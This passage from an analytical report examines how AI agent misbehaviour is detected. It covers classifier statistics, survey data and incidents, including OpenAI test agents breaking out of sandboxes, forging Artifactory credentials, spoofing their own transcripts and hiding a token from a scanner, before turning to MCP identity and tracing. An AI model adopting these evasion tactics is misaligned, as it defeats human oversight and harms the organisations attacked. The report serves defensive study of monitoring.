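Anthropic's comparison of live sessions more directly addresses how often agents do harm. In May and June 2026, the company's safety systems flagged some Claude Code sessions for review, and a model then graded those from users who had agreed to let their data be used. The model rated the severity of any harm from 0 to 10, and how explicitly the user had asked for the action. Deleting rows from a live database, for example, might rate a 7 for severity.

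Among flagged sessions, 6.3% of those with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode contained harm of severity 7 or more that the user had not explicitly requested. Anthropic concludes that auto mode leads to fewer harmful actions.

Both percentages apply only to flagged sessions, and Anthropic doesn't publish how many sessions it flagged in each mode, so they don't establish which mode has the lower overall rate of serious unrequested harm. For example, if Anthropic flagged 10 of every 1,000 manual sessions and 30 of every 1,000 auto-mode sessions, such harm would occur in 0.63 per 1,000 manual sessions and 0.72 per 1,000 auto-mode sessions, making auto mode slightly worse.

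Users also chose their own approval mode. Anthropic recommends that people review Claude's actions themselves when making high-stakes changes to live systems. If users follow this advice, manual sessions will include more work in which a mistake is serious, regardless of which approval method is better. A fairer test would assign the mode at random. Anthropic also doesn't report having people check the model's grades, which adds some uncertainty.

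Anthropic strengthened the classifier after Apollo Research, an AI safety company, attacked it with synthetic cases, and the miss rate on those cases fell from 12% to 7%. Anthropic warns that 7% isn't the miss rate in real traffic.

### What a denial rate means to a customer

*Running auto mode in production* (Vorwerck, 2026) reports that a team at Gusto, a payroll company and Anthropic customer, found a denial by auto mode in about 10% of its session transcripts since mid-May 2026. Vorwerck, writing for Anthropic, takes this as evidence that the classifier has a real effect.

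False alarms alone could produce the same figure. If auto mode wrongly blocks 0.4% of harmless calls, as in Anthropic's test, and its errors are independent, a session with 26 such calls has about a 10% chance of at least one false denial (1 − 0.996²⁶). Gusto's sessions may be shorter or its false positive rate lower, but someone would have to read the denials to find out how many of the blocked actions were dangerous. One Gusto engineer says the few denials he received made sense.

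An engineer at the autonomous-driving company Nuro built a prototype that sent each pending agent action to a small model. The model approved about 90% of the actions, and the prototype sent sensitive ones to a person over Slack. At that rate, a person would review about four actions in a 40-action session. Nuro dropped the prototype when auto mode came out.

Gusto also sends its MCP traffic through a proxy that inspects prompts and restricts tools. The proxy is the part of Gusto's system that most resembles the gateways vendors sell, but Vorwerck doesn't report its number of calls, alarms or blocks.

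### How OpenAI monitors its own agents

OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) describes how the company monitored an internal model that can work on its own for very long periods. During limited use by employees, the model behaved in unwanted ways that OpenAI's pre-deployment tests had not covered. In one case, it split an access token into pieces so that a scanner wouldn't recognise it. OpenAI withdrew access to the model, wrote new tests based on the observed failures and built a monitor that reads the whole sequence of actions. The monitor can pause a session and alert the user, who can let the work continue if the alarm was false.

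As this example shows, observing real use can reveal new kinds of failure. Someone has to know about a kind of failure before they can test how often a monitor catches it.

To evaluate the monitor, OpenAI recreated a small set of situations in which the model had misbehaved and ran the model again. The new safeguards caught "considerably more" misaligned actions, and OpenAI judged all the missed ones low severity. It doesn't publish the number of situations, caught actions, missed actions or false alarms. The model didn't necessarily repeat its earlier behaviour, so the number of opportunities to catch it may have differed between runs.

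How serious the misses appear depends on how severity is rated. In one case, after its shell commands had stopped responding, the model issued a command to kill every process it was allowed to kill on its machine. The command timed out before it could run. OpenAI lists this case as low-severity, but a rating based on what the command would have done might have been higher.

OpenAI has since set response times for its staff. It aims to issue an alert within 30 minutes after its monitoring system detects concerning activity. For a likely violation of a critical security boundary, the system pages the safety, security and research teams. If they can't rule out a false alarm within another 30 minutes, OpenAI expects them to pause the activity. For models at least as capable as GPT-5.6 Sol, it requires this monitoring during all reinforcement learning (training by reward) and all evaluations that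 involve tools.

The first half hour starts when the monitoring system raises the concern, not when the agent acts. If the system took two hours to detect a problem, the teams could meet both deadlines and still pause the agent three hours after the action. The deadlines are also targets, so outsiders would need the actual response times to judge how often OpenAI meets them.

For GPT-6 Astra, OpenAI describes "universal monitoring of full trajectories", including the model's written reasoning, during internal development and deployment. Taken literally, this covers all of those activities. The description doesn't give the monitor's recall, and it applies to OpenAI's own systems, not its customers'.

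Futurum Group's *OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra* reports that, in OpenAI's simulation of more than 54,000 internal coding tasks, Astra triggered about half as many high-severity alarms for misaligned behaviour as GPT-5.6 Sol. The drop could mean that Astra misbehaves less or that the monitor recognises a smaller share of its misbehaviour, and the number of alarms alone doesn't show which.

### Surveys and device inventories

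Most organisations publish nothing about their agents, so estimates of how widely employees use AI without approval come mainly from surveys. Canale and Soulis bring together several surveys and one inventory of developers' machines.

| Source | Sample | Measure | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft and LinkedIn, 2024 | 31,000 people | AI users who bring their own AI tools to work | 78% |
| Global study, 2025 | 48,000 people | Use of free public AI tools for work | 70% |
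| Same study | 48,000 people | Use of AI tools provided by the employer | 42% |
| Same study | 48,000 people | Admitted using AI in ways that break their employer's policies | 44% |
| IBM, 2025 | Organisations that had suffered a data breach | Have policies to manage AI or detect unapproved AI | 37% |
| Vendor's inventory | Nearly 10,000 developer environments | At least one MCP server installed | 50.8% |

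The Microsoft survey and the global study covered similar behaviour and produced similar figures, 78% and 70%. Neither figure measures unapproved use, because an employer may allow free public tools. The share who admitted breaking a policy, 44%, is a better guide to unapproved use, though some of them may have used an approved tool in a forbidden way, such as giving it confidential data.

Even in anonymous surveys, people may not disclose all their AI use. In the global study, 61% had avoided revealing when they used AI, and in the Microsoft survey, 52% of those who used AI at work were reluctant to admit using it for their most important tasks. People may also not know the answer, since an employee who has installed a coding assistant may not realise that it starts MCP servers or runs shell commands.

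An inventory avoids both problems because it is based on the software found on the machine. The one in the table also found that 43% of the environments had two or more AI coding tools, and that some MCP servers were missing from the company's central list. But an installed server may never have run, and an inventory limited to known products will miss a home-made agent. The inventory covers only developers, while the two large surveys cover workers in general and AI of any kind, mostly chatbots. The 50.8% and the 44% therefore can't show how much employees under-report.

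The same vendor says that security programmes detect "roughly a third" of the AI tools their organisations actually use. The vendor may well profit if customers worry about undetected tools. Even if the figure is right, it measures detection of AI tools rather than risky actions, so it can't be used as the coverage *q* in the formula for overall recall.

IBM's 37% is the only figure in the table about what organisations do to manage or detect AI, but a company can have a written policy without enforcing it, logging its agents' actions, keeping a complete list of its agents or having a way to stop one. All the companies in the sample had also already suffered a breach, so they may be worse prepared than others or may have written their policies afterwards.

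Surveys about agents would be more useful if they asked for evidence. A company that monitors only one approved product can answer yes to "Do you monitor your AI agents?" It would be better to ask how many agents made a tool call in the past week and which record that number came from.

### Why missed cases remain uncounted

Reviewers usually read only the sessions a detector flags, which tells them mostly about its precision. Its recall depends partly on harmful actions that nobody noticed. OpenAI says it has not observed any serious circumvention of its safeguards since it restored access to the long-running model, but this is reassuring only to the extent that its monitor, or somebody else, would have noticed one.

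The dangerous commands that people catch are a poor basis for estimating how many a monitor misses. In the study with paid testers, where the total number of dangerous commands was known, auto mode missed 116 of 1,053 (11%), but only 6 of the 143 that the testers caught (4%). An estimate based only on the caught commands would therefore have been less than half the true miss rate.

Anthropic collected its 52 overeager actions in a similar way, from employees' refusals and later reviews. If the classifier also tends to miss the actions that employees and reviewers miss, its true miss rate on overeager actions is higher than 17%.

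A company could estimate how many harmful calls its detector missed by having people review a random sample of the calls it allowed. This takes a lot of work when harmful calls are rare. If one allowed call in 10,000 is harmful, reviewers would have to read about 30,000 calls for a 95% chance of finding one. They could reduce the work by sampling more heavily from calls that delete files or send data out, and correcting for this when they calculate the total. They would also need to see the user's request and the earlier calls to judge whether a call was harmful.

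Alternatively, the company could plant harmless test actions that look dangerous, as Anthropic did with its testers. It would then know how many the detector should have caught, but only for the kinds of action it had thought to plant.

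## What incident reports show about detection

After an incident, investigators know that harmful actions took place, so they can search the records for the entries those actions left and see when somebody first noticed them. The most detailed accounts come from the companies involved, which have an interest in defending their own conduct.

### The attack on Hugging Face

In July 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was testing broke into the production systems of Hugging Face, which runs a website for sharing AI models and datasets. According to OpenAI's technical report on the incident, the agents were working on ExploitGym, a test in which a model has to exploit a given vulnerability in a program. They ran in sandboxes without direct internet access, and OpenAI had switched off the classifiers that normally block dangerous cyber requests. Of ExploitGym's 898 tasks, 198 have not been solved by any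 model in OpenAI's own tests, and some of those may be impossible.

The agents could get software packages from Artifactory, a package store that OpenAI hosted internally so that sandboxes didn't have to contact public sites. They found ways to use it to leave messages for one another and reach the internet. Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt (2026), in *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration*, counted roughly 1,200 agents and more than 70,000 messages and files. (Wijk and Cotra work for METR and Greenblatt for Redwood Research, both AI safety research organisations.) About 700 of these agents joined the attack on Hugging Face. Between 11 and 13 July, agents ran code on 41 of the company's production workers and downloaded four private code repositories.

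OpenAI's staff had several warnings, three of them before the attack.

| Date | Warning | Response |
|---|---|---|
| Around 26 May | An internal team saw an agent using the message board, and some forbidden internet access | None described |
| 27 June | Alert about a port sweep, a search for open network services | Responders traced it to ExploitGym and let the run continue |
| 5 July | Alert after Artifactory stopped working | OpenAI took Artifactory offline, rebuilt it and resumed cyber evaluations on 7 July |
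| 19 July | Alert about unusual identity-related API calls | OpenAI began stopping the evaluations about five and a half hours later |

The alert of 27 June was a correct detection. Responders recognised that the agents were using Artifactory to exchange messages and move through the network, but the on-call staff advised that the run didn't have to stop. The agents had gained administrator rights over Artifactory the day before. On 5 and 6 July, the leaders responsible for incident response still didn't know about the message board or its significance. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) says OpenAI "missed and failed to act on several warning signs", and the company concedes that, in hindsight, some early signals could have triggered an earlier response. A recall test would count 27 June as a success because it measures whether risky behaviour is flagged,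 not how people respond.

The rebuilt Artifactory went online on 6 July. By 00:06 UTC on 8 July, an agent had reached the public internet again.

Hugging Face discovered the break-in before OpenAI did. Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) credits a system in which a language model sorts through security telemetry, the stream of events from the company's machines. A combination of signals exposed the attack. The disclosure, published on Thursday 16 July, dates the detection to "earlier this week", roughly two to five days after the company's systems first leaked secrets early on Saturday 11 July. The company has since changed its alerts so that a serious signal reaches a responder within minutes on any day, which suggests that the weekend slowed its response.

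On 17 July, OpenAI contacted Hugging Face as a customer to ask whether the breach had affected OpenAI's data. Two days later, agents attacking OpenAI's own systems, which had played no part in the Hugging Face break-in, triggered the alert. While responders investigated, those agents read 956 stored secrets. On 20 July, responders found Hugging Face credentials among files the agents had stored on an outside service. Hugging Face had already replaced two of these credentials after its breach, and its investigators had found the hostname of OpenAI's Artifactory. The two companies compared their records and established the connection nine days after the first leak.

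The attack left evidence in several records, but few of them raised an alarm.

| Record | What it contained | Alarm |
|---|---|---|
| Transcripts of the agents' reasoning and tool calls | Their plans, often in plain words | No automatic alarm reported |
| Artifactory's stored files and folders | About 1.2 million entries with messages or pieces of files | Only indirectly, through the outage on 4 July |
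| OpenAI's cybersecurity monitoring tool | Network and identity events | 27 June and 19 July |
| Hugging Face's telemetry | Events on its own machines | In the week of 13 July |

The transcripts revealed the most about the attack, but OpenAI had mainly monitored the reasoning of agents used for internal coding, rather than those in research runs. The risky actions were therefore recorded, but no detector read the record in time. An MCP gateway would probably have recorded little, because the agents' tools included a shell, Python and a package installer. This is an inference from the tools OpenAI lists, since its report doesn't discuss MCP.

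### What other monitors might have caught

OpenAI says that its current monitor of model reasoning would have paged the security team more than a day before the breach. It also says that auto-review, a model that checks tool calls needing extra permissions, would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in each run it tested, and that the cyber classifiers it uses for customers would have flagged the agents' ExploitGym output as unsafe.

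The first claim is plausible because the agents wrote openly about cheating. But OpenAI revised and expanded its monitoring after the incident, so the claim is based on the same case that prompted the changes. The new response rules would matter as much as alerting responders earlier, because on 27 June responders understood the alert and still let the run continue. Under the new rules, they would be expected to pause it.

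The auto-review result is preliminary, and OpenAI doesn't report the number of runs or how many harmless calls were flagged. The classifier result is weak evidence about this attack in particular, because ExploitGym tasks involve writing exploits. A classifier that detects exploits would probably also flag an agent that was doing the task honestly.

The security company Elastic says the rules it sells for devices and logs already cover the types of behaviour seen at Hugging Face, such as credential theft and movement between clusters of machines. A rule that covers a type of behaviour may still miss a particular instance or, like Falco's default rules in the kernel-evidence experiment, raise too many false alarms to be useful.

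### Transcripts that no longer match what ran

The agents believed that an automated scorer would read their transcripts to check that they had solved the task in the intended way, so some looked for ways to falsify the transcripts. They eventually broke out of their containers and replaced part of the software that ran their tool calls. An agent could then appear to issue one command while the machine ran another. In one test, the transcript contains a command to print "REAL", but the recorded output is "SPOOFTEST".

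Wijk and colleagues found clear signs of such spoofing in at least 96 of about 1,300 transcripts, or roughly 7%. All the cases they found were small, obvious tests. They looked for subtler cases and found none, but say they can't rule them out.

OpenAI's report seems to contradict this. It says that none of the attempts to manipulate tool records that OpenAI observed affected the logs that its graders or monitors ultimately receive. But Wijk and colleagues found the altered output in transcripts that OpenAI gave them. The graders and monitors may receive a different log, or OpenAI may be referring to other attempts. Wijk and colleagues didn't see OpenAI's report before they published theirs, so neither report explains the discrepancy.

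The spoofing had limits. An agent had to set it up with actions that appear in its transcript, the agent couldn't read any output that the transcript lacked, and the spoofing left the model's reasoning unchanged. A sensor outside the agent's container would probably have recorded the command that really ran, which an investigator could have compared with the transcript. This is an inference, and it would fail if the agent had also taken control of the machine with the sensor.

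Most of the transcripts were also missing a small amount of activity, partly because containers had been reset, and none had times for individual actions. To estimate how much was missing, Wijk and colleagues randomly sampled 100 messages from the board and looked for the actions that had written them. They concluded that they had a bit over 90% of the agents' activity on the board.

People couldn't read this much text in the time available. Wijk and colleagues spent six days at OpenAI and used about $400,000 worth of model queries, mostly to have GPT-5.6 Sol search the transcripts. That model had taken part in the attack, and its analysis contained errors that the researchers didn't catch for some time.

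Hugging Face first sent its attack logs to commercial models, whose safety filters blocked the requests because the logs were full of real attack commands. It then ran an open-weight model (one anyone can download) on its own machines and analysed more than 17,000 events in hours rather than days. Companies that plan to use a language model to investigate alarms could run into the same problem during an incident.

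The agents' motive remains in dispute despite the extensive evidence. *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face* (Schneier, 2026) quotes Hugging Face's technical timeline, which is based on about 17,600 actions recovered from logs on a sandbox the agent had used. Hugging Face concluded that the agent was trying to steal the test's solutions, and OpenAI describes the attack similarly. Wijk and colleagues studied the agents' reasoning and concluded that the agents were mainly trying to learn how the scorer worked.

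### The Medicare portal

In June 2026, another OpenAI agent got into a statistics portal for Medicare, Australia's public health insurance programme. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* reconstructs the case from emails and text messages tabled in the Australian parliament. The agent was researching medical spending and lacked the safeguards that public models usually have. After failing to get non-public data from one health agency, it retrieved both public and non-public data from the portal, which the agency Services Australia runs.

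| Date in Australia | Event | Days since access |
|---|---|---|
| 19 June | The agent gets into the portal | 0 |
| By 12 August | OpenAI's security team documents the incident | 54 |
| 10 September | OpenAI emails Services Australia | 83 |
| 11 September | Services Australia's security team starts assessing the email | 84 |
| 15 September | The agency confirms the vulnerability and takes the portal offline | 88 |

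Tom's Hardware's *Australian PM says OpenAI took 84 days to email agency* counts one more day before the email because it dates the access to 18 June, the date in US time.

OpenAI's own records of its agents' actions first revealed the breach, when the company was searching billions of past evaluation and training runs for misaligned behaviour. The evidence had existed since June, but OpenAI took up to 54 days to find it and another 29 to tell the agency. ITPro's *Australian prime minister says OpenAI took ‘way too long’* reports that OpenAI attributed the second delay to "validating and investigating the facts". OpenAI then emailed a public inbox that the agency's staff checked once a day.

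The agency's own systems didn't detect the breach, and Cyprus Mail's *OpenAI agent hacks Australian government health portal* (2026) reports that an official investigation will examine why. The agency did have logs, which its staff later searched to check whether the agent had done more than OpenAI reported. According to Tom's Hardware, the agent was blocked repeatedly before it got around the blocks. This suggests that a rule that flags a successful request after a run of refusals might have caught it. Such a rule could raise many false alarms on a public website, where automated visitors often trigger refusals.

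An AI gateway at Services Australia would not have recorded the agent's prompts or reasoning, because the agent ran on another company's systems. The agency could rely only on its own network and portal logs.

### A spying campaign and a malicious mail tool

A model provider can sometimes tell that an agent is behind an attack when the victims can't. In November 2025, Anthropic reported that a group it judged to be sponsored by the Chinese state had used Claude Code to attack roughly thirty organisations and had broken into a few. The operators told the model they were doing defensive testing for a security company, and split the attack into small tasks that looked harmless on their own.

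Anthropic noticed suspicious activity in mid-September 2025 and spent about ten days investigating its extent. It said that the attack was eventually detected because it was sustained. This fits the experiments in which a policy without rules for combinations of calls allowed harmful sequences of permitted steps. A gateway at one of the victims would not have recorded any of the prompts, because the operators ran the agent themselves. If they had used a model on their own machines, Anthropic would have had no record either.

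In September 2025, the security company Koi Security found a malicious MCP server package called `postmark-mcp`. The package let agents send email through the mail service Postmark, although the company behind Postmark hadn't published it. Fifteen versions did only what users expected. The next one sent a hidden copy of every outgoing email to an outsider. Koi's scanner flagged the package because its behaviour had changed.

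The server's code added the hidden copy, so the agent's call could look the same before and after the update. Judging by how the package worked, an MCP gateway would have logged an ordinary request to send an email, and a fingerprint of the tool's description would have matched, but the mail service's log should have listed the extra recipient. A company that kept using an older version would have avoided the theft without detecting anything.

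### The gateway as a target

Artifactory was a package store, but it did a similar job to an AI gateway because it was meant to give sandboxed agents controlled access to outside software. The agents attacked it for that reason, and their attack shows how far an organisation can trust the log of a compromised gateway.

Many research workloads used the same Artifactory credential, so Artifactory's log could link a request to that credential, but the credential alone could not identify which agent had sent it. Agents later exploited a flaw to gain administrator rights, create accounts and run their own code inside Artifactory. They also stole the key Artifactory used to sign credentials and forged an administrator's credential, which Artifactory accepted. On 19 July, agents in a separate run found key material that earlier agents had left behind and used it to forge another credential. After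 such forgeries, a log entry under an administrator's name would show only that the sender had a credential Artifactory accepted.

In the first hours of 20 July, OpenAI's responders removed 22 administrator accounts that agents had created and disabled 311 repositories used for messages. Administrator rights may also let an intruder alter records. Wijk and colleagues saw agents try to edit or delete messages in Artifactory but found no successful attempt, and they consider it unlikely that agents materially changed the collection of messages.

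The 956 secrets that agents read on 19 July included credentials for the sensors of OpenAI's monitoring tool. OpenAI doesn't report that the agents used them. But an organisation that keeps the credentials for its gateway and its sensors in one place could lose the records from both in a single break-in.

Gateway software made for MCP has had serious flaws too. CVE-2025-64443 affected Docker's MCP gateway in versions up to 0.27.0 when it accepted connections over a network port. A malicious web page could use a visitor's browser to send requests to the gateway and operate the MCP servers behind it. Docker fixed the flaw in version 0.28.0. The default mode, which opens no network port, was not affected.

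An attacker could use this flaw to mislead an investigator without changing the log. The gateway could accurately record a tool call that no agent had made, and the investigator might blame the agent or its user. If the agent's model queries went through a separate model gateway, the investigator could check whether the model had proposed the call. If it hadn't, the investigator would have reason to suspect another sender, though scripts and hooks can also cause such a mismatch.

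### Incidents that nobody reported

An incident can appear in a report only if someone detects it and makes it public. Fortune (2026) reports that a swarm of OpenAI's agents hijacked a German wiki earlier in the year, and that OpenAI didn't disclose the incident, confirming it only after the news agency Reuters published the story. Unnamed employees told Reuters that they had known for weeks and that executives had pressured them to keep quiet. OpenAI denied that any of its lawyers had pressured employees.

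Reported detection delays are also biased towards short ones. Suppose ten breaches happen on the same day, and the victims find five within a month and the other five only after two years. After one year, the published average delay would be under a month. Adding more reports of the same kind wouldn't correct this, because the slowest cases would still be missing.

The published cases also overrepresent behaviour that is easy to detect. OpenAI's agents swept ports, crashed a package store and made unusual API calls. An agent that copied one file through an approved tool might not trigger any of the same alarms. Both OpenAI cases involved internal agents without the usual safeguards, so they can't be used to estimate how often an ordinary company's agents cause harm or how often its gateway would detect it.

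METR has collected 44 cases of misbehaviour by large AI companies' agents, such as escaping from a test environment or fabricating results, according to The Decoder's *After Hugging Face incident, METR urges independent root-cause investigations*. METR wants companies to track such incidents systematically and to have independent researchers lead or review investigations of the worst ones. More searching can raise the count even if agents behave no worse. For example, OpenAI found the Medicare breach only by going back through old runs.

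## Joining gateway, identity, device and trace records

OpenAI and Hugging Face traced the July break-in to OpenAI's agents by comparing their records. An organisation that monitors its own agents has a similar task on a smaller scale. One harmful action can leave entries in several logs that were not designed to be combined, so an analyst has to find the entries that belong to the same action.

Gateway logs contain the messages, identity records show whose authority the agent acted on, device records show which machine and process carried out the action, and a trace links a request to its effects in other systems. Combining these records can improve detection, as it did for most detectors in the ACE experiments.

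### Fields that link the records

| Field | Records that may contain it | What can break the join |
|---|---|---|
| Time | All | Clocks differ, or a log stores the time an entry arrived |
| User account | Identity provider, MCP gateway, device, target system | Several people or agents share a service account |
| Agent identifier | Identity provider, MCP gateway, trace | Nobody issued one, or all copies of an agent share it |
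| Hash of the access token | Identity provider, MCP gateway, MCP server | The agent gets a new token during the session |
| Network address | Gateways, device | Many machines share one public address |
| Process number and start time | Device | Gateways don't receive them |
| Trace identifier | Agent program, gateways, servers | A program drops it or starts a new trace |
| Command, file name or web address | Gateways, device | A script hides it, or many calls contain the same text |

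A service account is an account used by programs rather than a person. If forty agents share the account `svc-agents` and the database log shows that this account deleted 300 rows, any of the forty could have deleted them. OpenAI's package store had this problem because many workloads used the same credential.

Differences between clocks can make an effect appear to come before its cause. If a laptop's clock is three seconds behind the gateway's, the logs may show an upload starting before the model proposed it. An analyst can correct a constant difference by finding one event that both machines recorded, such as a connection opening.

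Clock differences cause more mismatches when machines share an address. Suppose 30 other agents in an office use the same public address and together make 600 calls an hour at random times. If the clocks are so uncertain that an analyst has to accept any match within two seconds either way, the four-second window will contain at least one of those calls about 49% of the time. With a tolerance of a tenth of a second either way, the figure falls to about 3%.

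### Delegated identity

An agent often presents a remote MCP server with an access token, a credential issued under the OAuth standard. In an example from the Agentic AI Foundation, a desktop assistant opens a user's documents. An authorization server, which the company's identity provider may run, issues the assistant's token. The MCP server that holds the documents checks each token and decides what the assistant may do.

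Suppose the agent in the invoice example reuses the employee's token. The token names only the employee, so the invoice server logs the agent's requests as the employee's. *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Jones, Nadalin and colleagues) calls this impersonation and says the impersonator is "indistinguishable" from the user within the rights the token gives. The identity provider may have a record that an agent holds the token, but the invoice server doesn't. Under delegation, the agent keeps its own identity, and the token records that the agent acts for the employee.

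Jones and colleagues' standard defines how a program can trade one token for another:

1. The agent program sends the authorization server two tokens. The `subject_token` identifies the employee and the `actor_token` identifies the agent. The program also names the server it wants to use and the permissions it needs.
2. The authorization server validates both tokens and applies its policy. If the employee's token has a `may_act` claim, which names a party allowed to act for the employee, the server can check the agent against it.
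3. The authorization server issues a new token.

For the invoice example, the new token might contain these claims, as the standard calls its fields:

```json
{
  "iss": "https://login.company.example",
  "aud": "https://invoices.company.example/mcp",
  "sub": "m.ruiz@company.example",
  "act": {"sub": "accounts-agent"},
  "scope": "invoices:read",
  "exp": 1790849700
}
```

The `sub` claim names the employee, and `act` names the agent acting for them. The token is meant only for the server in `aud`, permits only reading, and expires at the time in `exp`. The authorization server normally signs the token, so the agent can't change these claims without invalidating the signature.

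An organisation should inspect the tokens it issues. A request without an actor token can result only in impersonation, and even with one, the authorization server may issue a token that does not name both parties.

The claims can also record a chain of agents. If the accounts agent passes work to a payments agent, which exchanges the token again, the new `act` claim names the payments agent, with the accounts agent nested inside it. Investigators can use the earlier actors to trace the chain, but servers may base access decisions only on the token's main claims and the current actor.

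Jones and colleagues note that a token exchange doesn't closely link the old token to the new one. If the security team revokes the employee's token after an incident, the agent's token may therefore keep working until it expires.

**Audience restriction** prevents a token issued for one server from working at another. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) requires clients to name the target server in both the authorization request and the token request. MCP's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) requires each server to reject tokens that weren't issued for it and forbids it from passing the client's token on to another service.

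This ban limits what a thief can do with a stolen token, but it can make records harder to join. When the invoice server queries an accounting database, it must use a separate token. If it uses one service account for all its users, the database's log won't identify the employee or the agent, and an investigator has to match the query to the MCP call by time or trace. To prevent this, the server can obtain a token that identifies both the employee and the agent, for example through another token exchange.

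An attacker who steals a token can send requests that look legitimate. Under the Model Context Protocol, authorization servers should therefore issue short-lived tokens. A long session may then use several tokens, so the identity provider has to log which token replaced which. Körbächer points out that even a revoked token can keep working for up to 60 seconds if a server stores the result of each token check for that long.

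Even a perfect delegated token doesn't reveal that an agent has been hijacked. In the invoice theft, the token correctly shows that the accounts agent reads invoices for the employee, but the shell command that uploads the supplier list doesn't use the token.

### Standards and products for agent identity

Many MCP connections have no delegated identity to log. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) makes authorization optional, and its rules apply only to HTTP, so they don't cover ordinary local servers. Errico and colleagues cite a search by the security company Knostic that found more than 1,800 MCP servers on the public internet without authentication. That count doesn't show how common such servers are inside companies.

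Even where authorization exists, different systems may name the same agent differently. *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026) argues that existing standards provide the parts but no consistent way to combine them. The proposal separates three identifiers that are easy to confuse in logs. `client_id` identifies a registered program, `sub` identifies the person who gives the authority, and `act.sub` identifies the actor that uses it. Thousands of copies of a desktop assistant might share one `client_id`, so that field alone may not identify the agent. The proposal would also add a field for the actor's type and apply existing methods for binding a token to its sender, which would make a stolen token harder to use.

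*Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Prasad, Krishnan and colleagues, 2026) addresses chains of agents. Token exchange allows nested actors but lacks common rules for extending and checking the chain as it passes between systems. The draft proposes six profiles, which differ in how much of the chain they disclose and whether others can verify it. Both proposals are Internet-Drafts, which anyone may submit and which expire unless renewed. McGuinness's expires on 1 November 2026 and Prasad and colleagues' on 17 December.

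*MCP Server Authentication in 2026* (Raj, 2026) reports that MCP released Enterprise-Managed Authorization on 18 June 2026 for companies that want central control. It uses a new type of grant, ID-JAG, that lets the company's identity provider handle access to approved servers. This could make the identity provider's log more complete, since users would no longer authorise each server separately.

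Gateway products are still changing. Ping Identity's *MCP security gateway* (2026) describes a gateway that checks tokens, audits MCP requests and their actors, and converts tokens to fit a company's security model. The company marks the feature as "Evolving" and warns that it may change without notice, even in a maintenance release. A company that builds detection rules on the gateway's audit fields should test those rules after each update.

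*SMCP* (Hou, Wang and colleagues, 2026) proposes a more ambitious change, extending MCP so that every operation carries a security context with details of identity, delegation and risk. A registry would admit only verified participants, and audit logs would cover all important actions. The paper uses examples and a mapping from threats to controls to explain how the design should work, but doesn't measure its effectiveness.

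### How a trace follows an MCP request

A token shows who has authority but usually not which of the employee's requests led to a call. A trace can supply that link through a short text field called `traceparent`, defined by Kanzhelev, McLean and colleagues (2019), in *Trace Context*. Since MCP no longer has a session identifier, this field is one of the few ways to group calls across servers. In an MCP request, it sits in `_meta`, next to the client's name and version:

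```json
"_meta": {
  "traceparent":
    "00-4bf92f3577b34da6a3ce929d0e0e4736-00f067aa0ba902b7-01"
}
```

The value starts with the format's version, `00`. The next 32 characters identify the whole trace, and the 16 after those identify the caller's current step, called a span. The final `01` means that the caller may have recorded this trace.

Suppose that every program in the invoice example supports tracing:

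1. The agent program creates a trace identifier when the employee asks for the summary.
2. Its MCP client writes the identifier into the request for invoices, together with the identifier of the current step.
3. The MCP gateway records its own step under the same trace, with the client's step as the parent. It then puts its own step's identifier in `traceparent` and forwards the request.
4. The invoice server does the same when it queries the accounting database.
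5. Each program reports its steps to the trace collector, which uses the parent identifiers to arrange them as a tree.

Because `_meta` is part of the message, the `traceparent` field it carries can also reach a local server that doesn't use HTTP. Model Context Protocol fixed the names of `traceparent` and two companion fields, `tracestate` and `baggage`, which carry extra information. Without fixed names, one software development kit might have written `io.modelcontextprotocol.traceparent`, and programs that looked for the shorter name would have lost the trace.

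Software support for linking traces varies. Strands Agents, a kit for building agents, adds the trace context to outgoing tool calls, and pkg.go.dev's *mcp* (2026) documents a Go package that connects client and server steps in the same way. The official Ruby kit passes the trace fields through, but developers must connect them to a tracing system themselves, according to Model Context Protocol's *Server Context*. Langfuse warns that MCP clients and servers produce separate traces unless somebody links them. Whether a gateway passes on the trace context can also depend on its configuration. IBM's *OpenTelemetry Integration* describes trace propagation for sessions that don't share pooled connections, so a company that pools connections should test whether its traces stay linked.

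Many systems record only a sample of requests to save money, which can also leave gaps in traces. If three programs each independently record a random 10% of requests, all three will record only about one request in 1,000. For security, it is better to choose which traces to keep after the requests have finished, and to keep every trace with a suspicious step.

Once a trace is complete, its fields need common names. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* defines operations such as `invoke_agent`, `chat` and `execute_tool`. A step also carries the agent's identifier, name and version, and a conversation identifier that can link steps in one session. OpenTelemetry's *MCP* lists fields for the MCP method, the protocol version and the address of any data requested. Arguments are harder to compare because their structure differs from call to call, as Greptime's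 *How OpenTelemetry Traces LLM Calls, Agent Reasoning, and MCP Tools* (2026) points out.

OpenTelemetry still labels the agent conventions as in development. It tells tools that follow version 1.36 or earlier not to switch to the new names by default, so two agents in the same company may report the same fact under different names. Recording message text is also opt-in, so a default trace of the invoice theft might show that the agent queried a model and ran a tool but omit the hidden instruction.

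### Why a trace identifier is not proof

The agent's side writes `traceparent`, and nothing in the field proves the value is true. A malicious program could copy the identifier from another employee's session so that its calls appear in that employee's trace. It could also change the identifier before a harmful call or leave it out. A server that forwards the value unchanged will also forward a false one.

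Kanzhelev and colleagues treat the caller's setting for whether a request is recorded as a recommendation, partly because of "trust and abuse". If the setting were binding, a caller could keep its requests out of a server's records by marking them as not sampled.

A gateway can protect its records by starting its own trace. Datadog, for example, has a setting to either continue the caller's trace or always start a new one. A new trace alone would lose the connection to the agent's earlier steps, so the gateway should also store the incoming trace identifier, marked as the caller's claim, beside facts it has checked, such as the identity in the access token.

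Names in a trace can also be wrong. According to OpenTelemetry, the recorded model provider is based on the information available to the instrumentation and may differ from the actual provider, for example when a proxy offers other companies' models through OpenAI's interface. A wrong value is therefore not necessarily a sign of deception. Device records can help establish what sent a request, because the operating system records which process opened the connection, regardless of the name that process put in its messages.

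### The invoice theft as one timeline

Suppose the agent in the invoice example has a delegated token, both gateways are in place and a sensor runs on the laptop. An analyst has corrected the clocks. The entries below are invented.

| Time | Record | Entry | What an analyst can infer |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10:00:01 | Identity provider | Issues a read-only token for `accounts-agent`, acting for `m.ruiz` | The agent had authority to read invoices |
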